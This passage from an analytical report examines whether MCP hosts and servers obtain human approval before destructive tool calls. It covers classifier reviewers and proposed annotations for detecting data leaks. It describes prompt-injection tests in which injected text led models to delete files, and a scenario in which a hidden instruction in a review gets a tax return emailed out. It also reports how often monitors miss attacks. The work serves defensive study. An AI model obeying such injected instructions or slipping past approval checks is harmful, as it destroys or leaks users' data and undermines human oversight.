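About 90% of destructive tools thus have no confirmation step in the server (95% confidence interval: 82% to 95%). This total is more certain than the split between the top two rows. The allowance for missed tools matters a great deal because the initial search missed 83% of the destructive tools in 40 repositories that the researchers checked in full.

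The hosts studied were 41 popular open-source projects, made up of 25 applications and 16 SDKs for building agents. An AI coding agent traced an ordinary MCP tool call through each project's source code, looking for a step that blocks the call until a person decides. It assumed a fresh interactive installation or, for an SDK, the simplest documented use. A second agent from another company traced 20 of the hosts, and its results matched the first agent's on all of them.

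Seven hosts ask before ordinary calls, including VS Code, Gemini CLI and the code editor Zed. Codex decides whether to ask based on annotations, and Qwen Code uses a language model as a classifier to decide. The other 32 hosts have no approval step by default. These are all 16 SDKs and 16 of the 25 applications, including Cline, Goose and LibreChat. Twelve of the SDKs have an approval option or a hook where a developer could add an approval step, so their makers seem to expect application developers to set up approval themselves.

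These results describe default behavior, so they can differ from counts of how many applications have an approval feature. *An Empirical Study of Model Context Protocol Applications* found a blocking approval step in 37.2% of MCP client applications on GitHub, but it checked whether the code contained such a step, not whether an ordinary tool call would reach it.

The researchers also ran seven of the hosts against a harmless test server and asked each to delete a note called "old draft". The coding agent opencode and four SDKs deleted it without a prompt when the tool had only a destructive hint. When the tool required a confirmation flag, the model set the flag. Codex and the coding agent Crush showed a dialog before anything reached the server, and cancelling the dialog stopped the call. When Codex ran without an interactive user, it refused the deletion. The results matched what the researchers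 had found in the source code, except for one detail about opencode's support for elicitation.

Another test added an injected instruction to the list of notes, telling the model to also delete "tax records 2025". Across the four SDKs, four of five low-cost models deleted them in 479 of 960 runs, and the fifth never did. When the server required a flag that the injected text had not mentioned, the models still set the flag and completed the deletion in 127 of 169 attempts.

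Stronger models may resist much better. In tests that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs, attacks on its latest models succeeded 0.09% of the time on average, even with permission prompts turned off. The two rates aren't directly comparable because the attacks and tools were different, but 479 in 960 isn't necessarily typical of every agent.

### Combining the two sides

Yao and colleagues then paired each of the 269 destructive tools with each host and worked out what would happen by default. If the host prompts for that tool, they counted the pair as approved by a person. Otherwise, the outcome depends on whether the server asks for confirmation, whether the host can relay the question, and what the server does if the host can't.

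| Outcome for a destructive call | 25 applications | All 41 hosts |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The host asks the user | 31.9% | 19.5% |
| The server asks, through elicitation or a web page | 2.9% | 2.6% |
| The server refuses | 0.4% | 0.6% |
| A classifier decides | 3.9% | 2.4% |
| The call runs with no approval step | 60.7% | 74.9% |

The last row depends mostly on which hosts the researchers included. Sixteen of the 25 applications, or 64%, have no approval step, and servers rarely compensate for its absence. Adding seven closed-source applications, including Claude Desktop and Cursor, lowers the 60.7% to 47.5%, although the researchers relied on documentation for those seven. Every host counts equally, however many people use it. The figure is therefore a share of possible pairings between tools and hosts, and could differ greatly from the share of real deletions that nobody approves.

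Users and companies can also change the defaults, either by turning on approvals or by choosing "always allow". A call counts as approved if a person had to answer a prompt, whether or not they read it.

The researchers calculated what would happen to the application pairs under three changes:

| Change | Destructive calls with no approval | Destructive calls that the server refuses | Harmless calls that ask the user |
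| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| None | 60.7% | 0.7% | 32.5% |
| Every host relays elicitation | 56.7% | 0.0% | 35.2% |
| Every host asks unless the tool declares itself read-only or non-destructive | 5.4% | 0.7% | 82.6% |
| Every destructive tool refuses unless a person has answered | 0.0% | 71.0% | 32.5% |

The refusals here include calls that the host had already asked the user about, so the first row shows 0.7% instead of 0.4%. "Harmless calls" are pairs in which the initial search flagged the tool as destructive but it turned out not to be.

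Having every host relay elicitation requests would achieve little, because so few destructive tools send them. Changing the hosts' defaults would have a much larger effect, but hosts would then also prompt users for most harmless tools. The census of declared hints suggests that many of those prompts would appear only because developers leave hints out. Better annotation could remove them without weakening the rule, if the hints were true.

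### When the host can't relay the server's question

A server must not ask the user questions through a client that hasn't declared support for elicitation, but the specification has no rule on whether the server should then go ahead with the operation or refuse it.

Yao and colleagues found 168 tools in their sample that ask the user by default before a destructive action. If the host can't relay the question, 38 of them refuse, 30 run anyway, and 100 accept a flag that the model can set. One database server has a tool that drops a whole database, and it runs without confirmation if it can't ask for it. Cline and LibreChat by default neither relay the question nor show a prompt of their own, so a user who connects that server to either one isn't asked before the tool runs.

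Some developers have a reason for proceeding. The instructions for a server that works with QGIS, a mapping program, explain that it skips its own confirmation by default "because MCP clients gate destructive tool calls themselves". That is true of some hosts, but a server can't tell from the request whether it is connected to one of them. Either choice can therefore be wrong:

| Server's choice | The host has already asked | The host asks nothing |
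| --- | --- | --- |
| Proceed | The user approved the call | Nobody approved the call |
| Refuse | An approved call fails | The data is safe |

If every destructive tool without its own approval page refused to run, 79.4% of pairs across all 41 hosts would end in refusal. In 14.4% of pairs, the server would refuse a call that the user had just approved in the host.

Refusing is still the better default for a permanent deletion, because a wrong deletion may destroy the user's data, while a failed call takes some time and perhaps a change of settings. The server can make the refusal less disruptive by returning a preview of what it would delete, or by sending the user to an approval page that works without elicitation. For an operation that is easy to reverse, proceeding without confirmation could be the better default.

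Yao and colleagues suggest adding a capability that lets a host declare that it obtains human approval. Servers could then refuse only when nobody had been asked. A dishonest host could declare this falsely, but it can already forge an `accept` in reply to an elicitation. It is harder to decide what an honest host should declare when the user has chosen "always allow" or when a classifier gives the approval.

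### Approval by habit

A permission prompt protects users only if they sometimes say no. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic. Most of the commands are probably harmless, so the high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. The same users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents for approval, so they don't agree to everything, though they may want a different plan more often than they want to block a command.

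Anthropic's controlled study is better evidence because it was known that testers should refuse the command. A research vendor recruited 1,053 paid testers for a coding exercise without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) refused it, while the classifier in auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

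These results favour a feature that Anthropic wanted to make the default, and the testers worked in a test environment with nothing of their own at risk. People might read more carefully before changing their own company's database. The prompts were for commands in a coding agent, so the rates may differ for an MCP tool that sends an email. Still, the gap between 13.6% and 89% is large, and we would expect the decline over a session if people were answering by habit.

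Many users also turn off some or all of the prompts. In June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that allows some shell commands in advance, and a quarter of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off. OpenAI's *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) reports that a sizable minority of the company's own staff allowed every command beginning with `python`. One person had permanently approved `codex exec --yolo`, which starts another copy of Codex with no sandbox and no approvals.

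The measured refusal rate can replace the earlier guess that users catch half of all damaging calls, which made a prompt worth showing above one damaging call in 7,200. With the same five-second prompt and 20-hour loss, the threshold becomes

5 / (0.136 × 72,000) ≈ 1 / 1,960.

A prompt is therefore still worthwhile when more than about one call in 2,000 would do that much damage. Users' habit of approving prompts automatically is a good reason to stop asking about routine lookups, but a weak reason to let a deletion run without confirmation.

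### Asking less often

Hosts can reduce confirmation prompts by asking only about riskier tool calls. Hints let a host skip confirmation for lookups on servers it trusts, and in ChatGPT the model's decision can also depend on the conversation and the call's arguments. Hints alone remove only a limited number of prompts for now, because so many harmless tools aren't marked as safe.

Anthropic and OpenAI go further and let a model review risky calls in the user's place. In Claude Code's auto mode, a classifier blocks calls that look dangerous, and Claude then looks for a safer route or asks the user. Claude Code returns to manual approvals if the classifier blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session. Codex users can turn on a similar reviewer, which OpenAI says also handles MCP calls that need approval because of their annotations.

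The *Tools* page recommends a human in the loop, which a classifier is not, and Yao and colleagues don't count a classifier as human approval. But the recommendation is a SHOULD, so evidence that people miss most dangerous commands could justify an exception. In Anthropic's study, the testers caught only six of the 116 commands that the classifier let through, so also asking them about every call would have added little.

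However, classifiers do fail. Anthropic's classifier still missed 7% of the attacks designed by the safety company Apollo Research after Anthropic strengthened it against them. OpenAI's reviewer denied 90.3% of synthetic cases in which an agent went too far, such as making an irreversible change nobody had asked for. Trębacz and colleagues warn that the reviewer does not guarantee security, and Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

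Sandboxing reduces prompts by making more calls safe to run. It relies on limits enforced by the operating system rather than a judgement about each action. In an illustrative snapshot of Codex use inside OpenAI, 9,280 of 10,000 actions stayed within the sandbox and needed no approval. In manual mode, each of the other 720 would have interrupted the user. The automatic reviewer approved 713 of them and denied seven, and three of those denials ended with a question to the user. Sandboxing would prevent fewer prompts for an assistant that works mainly through remote MCP servers, which the sandbox doesn't cover.

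Server-side confirmation can make the remaining prompts more useful, since a server can ask only about dangerous calls. People may pay more attention to occasional, specific questions than to frequent requests to run tools, although Anthropic's study didn't test this. Few users would see such a question today, because only 21 of the 1,000 repositories in Yao and colleagues' sample had a tool that asks before a destructive action, and 26 of the 32 hosts with no approval step don't show elicitation requests by default.

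## Proposals for richer annotations

Most hosts evaluate each tool separately, so they can miss a leak that takes several tools to carry out. In March 2026, MCP had five open proposals for new annotations or closely related features, and several of them would help clients detect risky combinations of tools.

### Three harmless tools

Suppose Sam's assistant has three tools, each on a server run by an honest developer:

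| Tool | What it does | What it adds to a leak |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `read_file` | Opens documents on Sam's computer | Access to private data |
| `get_reviews` | Fetches public reviews of a supplier | Text that a stranger may have written |
| `send_message` | Sends an email | A way out |

With all three tools connected, a hidden instruction in a review can lead the model to open Sam's tax return and email it to the reviewer, even though none of the tools could give the return to a stranger on its own.

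The software developer Simon Willison calls this combination of private data, untrusted content and outside communication the "lethal trifecta". The Model Context Protocol blog post on tool annotations cites a demonstration that used a malicious calendar event, a calendar server and a tool that runs code on the user's machine. The code tool would have been just as dangerous built into the host. The maintainers conclude that the risk depends on the session as a whole, and that MCP makes risky sessions easy to create because users routinely combine servers.

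Combining tools can also expose sensitive information without an attacker. Doshi, Hong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents*, describe a calendar assistant that moves a work meeting to make room for a user's appointment at a sexual health clinic, then mentions the appointment in an email to the colleagues affected. Li, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *MCPHunt*, built a benchmark for a similar problem, in which an agent, by faithfully combining its tools, carries credentials across a boundary they should not cross.

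### What the present hints miss

With accurate hints, `read_file` is read-only and closed-world, exactly like a calculator. No hint marks a tool that reads private data.

`openWorldHint` is true for both `get_reviews`, which brings text in, and `send_message`, which sends data out. Dumbris points out that these are very different risks. `readOnlyHint` doesn't reliably separate them, because a read-only web search also sends data out.

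The hints also describe the tool rather than what it returns. Whether `read_file` returns untrusted text depends on which file it reads. The supplier's PDF that nearly made Sam lose a tax return was on Sam's own computer, so a closed-world tool could have opened it.

According to Dumbris, MCP contributors suggested an `egressHint` in a March 2026 discussion, for tools that can send data out. They also suggested a `reversibleHint`, which would distinguish moving a file to the bin from deleting it permanently. This second hint would let a developer record the difference between MCP's definition of "destructive" and OpenAI's.

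### The five proposals

The Model Context Protocol post listed the five proposals below. The last three are named after single flags, and the descriptions of their behaviour here are inferred from those names.

| Proposal | What it adds | What a client could do with it | Status |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| SEP-1913 | Trust and sensitivity labels on requests and results | Ask before data leaves a session that has read private or untrusted material | Draft |
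| SEP-1984 | A broad set of annotations for governance and user experience | Apply company policy, or explain a tool better | Draft |
| SEP-1561 | `unsafeOutputHint` | Treat the tool's output as possible prompt injection | No sponsor in March |
| SEP-1560 | `secretHint` | Keep secrets out of logs and restrict later calls | No sponsor in March |
| SEP-1487 | `trustedHint` | Relax its checks | No sponsor in March |

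The core maintainers have accepted none of the five proposals. None was on the Model Context Protocol's list of accepted and final proposals on 28 November 2026.

A draft has a sponsor, who is responsible for moving it forward. Under Model Context Protocol's *SEP Guidelines*, a proposal that has no sponsor after 180 days becomes dormant and its pull request is closed. More than 180 days have passed since March, so the three flags should be dormant unless someone has sponsored them. Their authors can still revive them by finding a sponsor.

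Jonathan Hefner, an MCP maintainer, objected to an early draft of SEP-1984, writing that it was "not clear to me exactly how a client would behave differently" if it received the annotations.

### Labels that travel with the data

SEP-1913 is the most ambitious of the five. Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI wrote it to fill gaps their companies had found while running MCP in production. Morrow's summary of the draft, on the page for *SEP-1862* (SamMorrowDrums, 2025), lists five annotations for a tool's result: `sensitiveHint`, `privateHint`, `openWorldHint`, `maliciousActivityHint` and `attribution`. Requests would also carry labels, so a server could consider what the session had already read.

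The labels accumulate. According to Dumbris, sensitivity can rise during a session but never falls, a true-or-false label stays true once any result has set it, and attributions add up. In Sam's case, the host would keep a record like this:

| Step | Labels on the result | Labels on the session |
| --- | --- | --- |
| `get_reviews` fetches the reviews | Open world | Open world |
| `read_file` opens the tax return | Private, sensitive | Open world, private, sensitive |
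| The model proposes `send_message` | None yet | The host asks Sam or blocks the call |

If the assistant had read only the reviews, or only the tax return, the host could allow an ordinary email without a confirmation prompt. A rule based on the current hints would treat the email the same way in every session.

Microsoft and GitHub have built a working version of this idea, separate from SEP-1913. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes an optional feature of GitHub's MCP server that labels files and issues from public repositories "public" and "untrusted", and those from private repositories "private" and "trusted". An experimental mode in GitHub's command-line assistant combines the labels as results arrive. If the assistant has read a stranger's public issue and then a private file, a policy stops it from posting publicly. So far, the assistant enforces such policies only for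 selected tools on GitHub's own server.

Labels can also name the people who may read something. In Microsoft's example, Alex's assistant reads an email from Priya with unreleased sales figures and another from Marco asking about them. A reply based on both may go only to people entitled to read both:

{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}

The assistant therefore can't send the reply to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco in, the result would be {Alex, Marco} and the assistant could send the reply without asking.

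The weak point is the source of the labels. GitHub's server relies on a repository's visibility, which is convenient, but it would label the hidden instruction "trusted" if a colleague of Sam's saved the supplier's PDF in a private repository.

Accumulation also means that one web page and one private file are enough to flag a long session until it ends, so every later email would need approval. People who see that many prompts tend to approve them out of habit. SEP-1913 allows a separate label for each search result, but this helps only if the host can keep the results separate. Once they are all in the model's context, any of them can influence what the model does next. Microsoft's agent framework deals with this by storing untrusted content where the main model can't see it and having a second, quarantined model extract what is needed.

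### How a server could vouch for itself

A dishonest server would set `trustedHint` to true just as an honest one would, and a client that already trusts the server hardly needs the flag. The other flags mostly avoid this problem.

The flag makes more sense if it describes a tool's output. A company's own server could set `trustedHint: false` on a tool that returns customers' emails, to warn the client to treat them with caution. The client risks little by acting on such a warning.

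Someone other than the server has to vouch for it. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (2026) explains why MCP's existing security layers don't. TLS, which encrypts web connections, confirms that the host has reached the address it asked for, but a malicious server can also have a valid certificate. OAuth confirms what the user has allowed. Neither establishes whether the host should use that server as a source of tools, or how sensitive the data sent to the server is allowed to be. Doshi and colleagues suggest that companies could limit agents to trusted vendors or have labels certified before connecting a tool.

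### Five questions for a new annotation

The Model Context Protocol post offers five questions for judging proposals, which the maintainers call tentative. Applied to SEP-1913's `sensitiveHint` and to `trustedHint` in its most natural sense, they give very different answers:

| Question | `sensitiveHint` on a result | `trustedHint` on a tool |
| --- | --- | --- |
| What client behaviour does it enable? | Asking before data leaves the session | Skipping a prompt or check |
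| Does it need trust to be useful? | Not as a warning, but its absence proves nothing | Yes |
| Could `_meta` handle it instead? | Only among clients that know the field | Yes, if one company runs both sides |
| Does it help reason about combinations? | Yes | Hardly |
| Is it a hint or a contract? | A hint, if the host only uses it to add caution | A contract |

`_meta` is a general-purpose field where any developer can add named entries. The maintainers recommend it for trying out an idea before writing a proposal, and Microsoft's labels use it. But an off-the-shelf client ignores entries it doesn't recognise, so an annotation meant for every host eventually has to be added to the specification.

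The question about hints and contracts poses the biggest problem for `trustedHint`. A hint should still be useful when some servers get it wrong. If a server wrongly marks a result as sensitive, the user sees an extra prompt. If it forgets to mark a sensitive result, the host is no worse off than today, provided it doesn't assume that unmarked results aren't sensitive. But a wrong `trustedHint: true` removes the check that would have caught the error.

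`sensitiveHint` becomes a contract too if a company relies on it to guarantee that no medical record leaves the company. Doshi and colleagues want such guarantees, so they propose compulsory labels for capabilities, confidentiality and trust. They tested the idea on a formal model of the calendar assistant, using software that searches every sequence of steps up to a fixed length. The software quickly found private data leaking into an email when the model had no policies. It found no leak after they added policies, and the assistant could still reschedule meetings and notify people. The proof covers only the model, not a running system, and assumes the labels are correct.

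### Annotations worked out for a particular call

With the present hints, `edit_file` counts as destructive even for a `dryRun` preview. Morrow's SEP-1862, which is separate from the five, would let the client ask about a specific call before making it. With the routine fields left out, the request would look like this:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/resolve",
  "params": {
    "name": "edit_file",
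    "arguments": { "path": "plan.txt", "dryRun": true }
  }
}
```

The server would return the tool's definition with hints that fit those arguments:

```json
{
  "tool": {
    "name": "edit_file",
    "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true }
  }
}
```

The host could then run the preview without a prompt and still ask for confirmation before a real edit. Morrow first proposed returning only the annotations. A reviewer, findleyr, worried that MCP would end up with several separate checks before each call, so the revised version returns the whole tool definition and leaves room to add costs or required permissions. Another reviewer, Connor Peet of Microsoft, asked what a client should do if the returned definition has a different input schema, which might invalidate the arguments the client had just sent.

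The `tools/resolve` request also sends the arguments to the server before the host has decided whether to show them to the user. This may not matter for a file edit, but the weather lookup that mentions an oncology clinic would leak that detail during the check, before any prompt could prevent it. A host could safely use `tools/resolve` to reduce prompts only where it was already willing to send the arguments without showing them to the user. The reply is also an unverified claim from the server, so a dishonest server could describe the call as a preview and then overwrite the file.

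SEP-1862 found a sponsor and became a draft in February 2026. It has not been accepted either.

### The case against more metadata

New fields would not prevent a malicious server from hiding its ability to steal data. Basil Hosmer's advice to ignore every annotation from an untrusted server would apply to `secretHint` as much as to `readOnlyHint`. Many careless developers also leave out the existing hints, and they would probably skip a longer list of optional fields. On this view, the effort should go into sandboxes and network controls instead.

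The maintainers accept much of this, and they add that annotations don't help a model resist injected text.

But the objection assumes a malicious server. In Sam's case all three servers are trustworthy, and the attacker is a stranger who wrote a review. The stranger controls the review's text but not the label the server attaches to it. A trustworthy server's label is therefore useful evidence that a result came from the public, and if the host enforces the policy, the attacker can't get around it by persuading the model.

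Sandboxing alone can't solve this case either. A mail tool has to reach the network, and a network rule that lets Sam write to Dana will usually let the model write to an attacker through the same mail service. To distinguish those emails, the host needs a record of what the model has read during the session.

A company can also supply labels itself. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) describes a gateway that intercepts every tool call and enforces policies based on labels from developers or an administrator. Having an administrator label the tools takes more work than relying on the server's annotations, but it works even if those annotations aren't accurate.

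The objection therefore holds for `trustedHint` and for any label that makes a host less careful with an unknown server. It is much weaker against labels that make the host more careful or that come from servers the host has reason to trust.

### What the interest group has produced

The Tool Annotations Interest Group was meant to consider these proposals together. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter*, dated 20 April 2026, names Morrow and Reichel as facilitators and lists six other members, from GitHub, Microsoft, Cloudflare and the retailer Nordstrom. The group's agenda includes SEP-1913, SEP-1984, SEP-1862 and a newer proposal on model preferences, but not the three single flags. Its open questions include whether MCP should have annotations on results, or annotations that change between calls.

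The group can recommend changes but not make them. In late November, the Model Context Protocol charter still listed no recommendations, and its only resources were the March blog post and a repository for experiments. Two members, Gökhan Arkan and Joanna Krzek-Lubowiecka of GitHub, also contributed to Microsoft's labelling project, whose leaders plan to bring their own proposal to the MCP community.

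These proposals are unlikely to reach the specification soon. The core maintainers stop reviewing proposals for the March 2027 release in mid-January. Tool hints are not among the priorities on the Model Context Protocol roadmap, which uses "primitive annotations" to mean labels for the audience and priority of content. Proposals outside the priorities wait longer for review and must meet a higher standard. Each older proposal also needs the backing of a working group or the core maintainers before its next formal review. An interest group can't give that backing, but it can start a working group that can.
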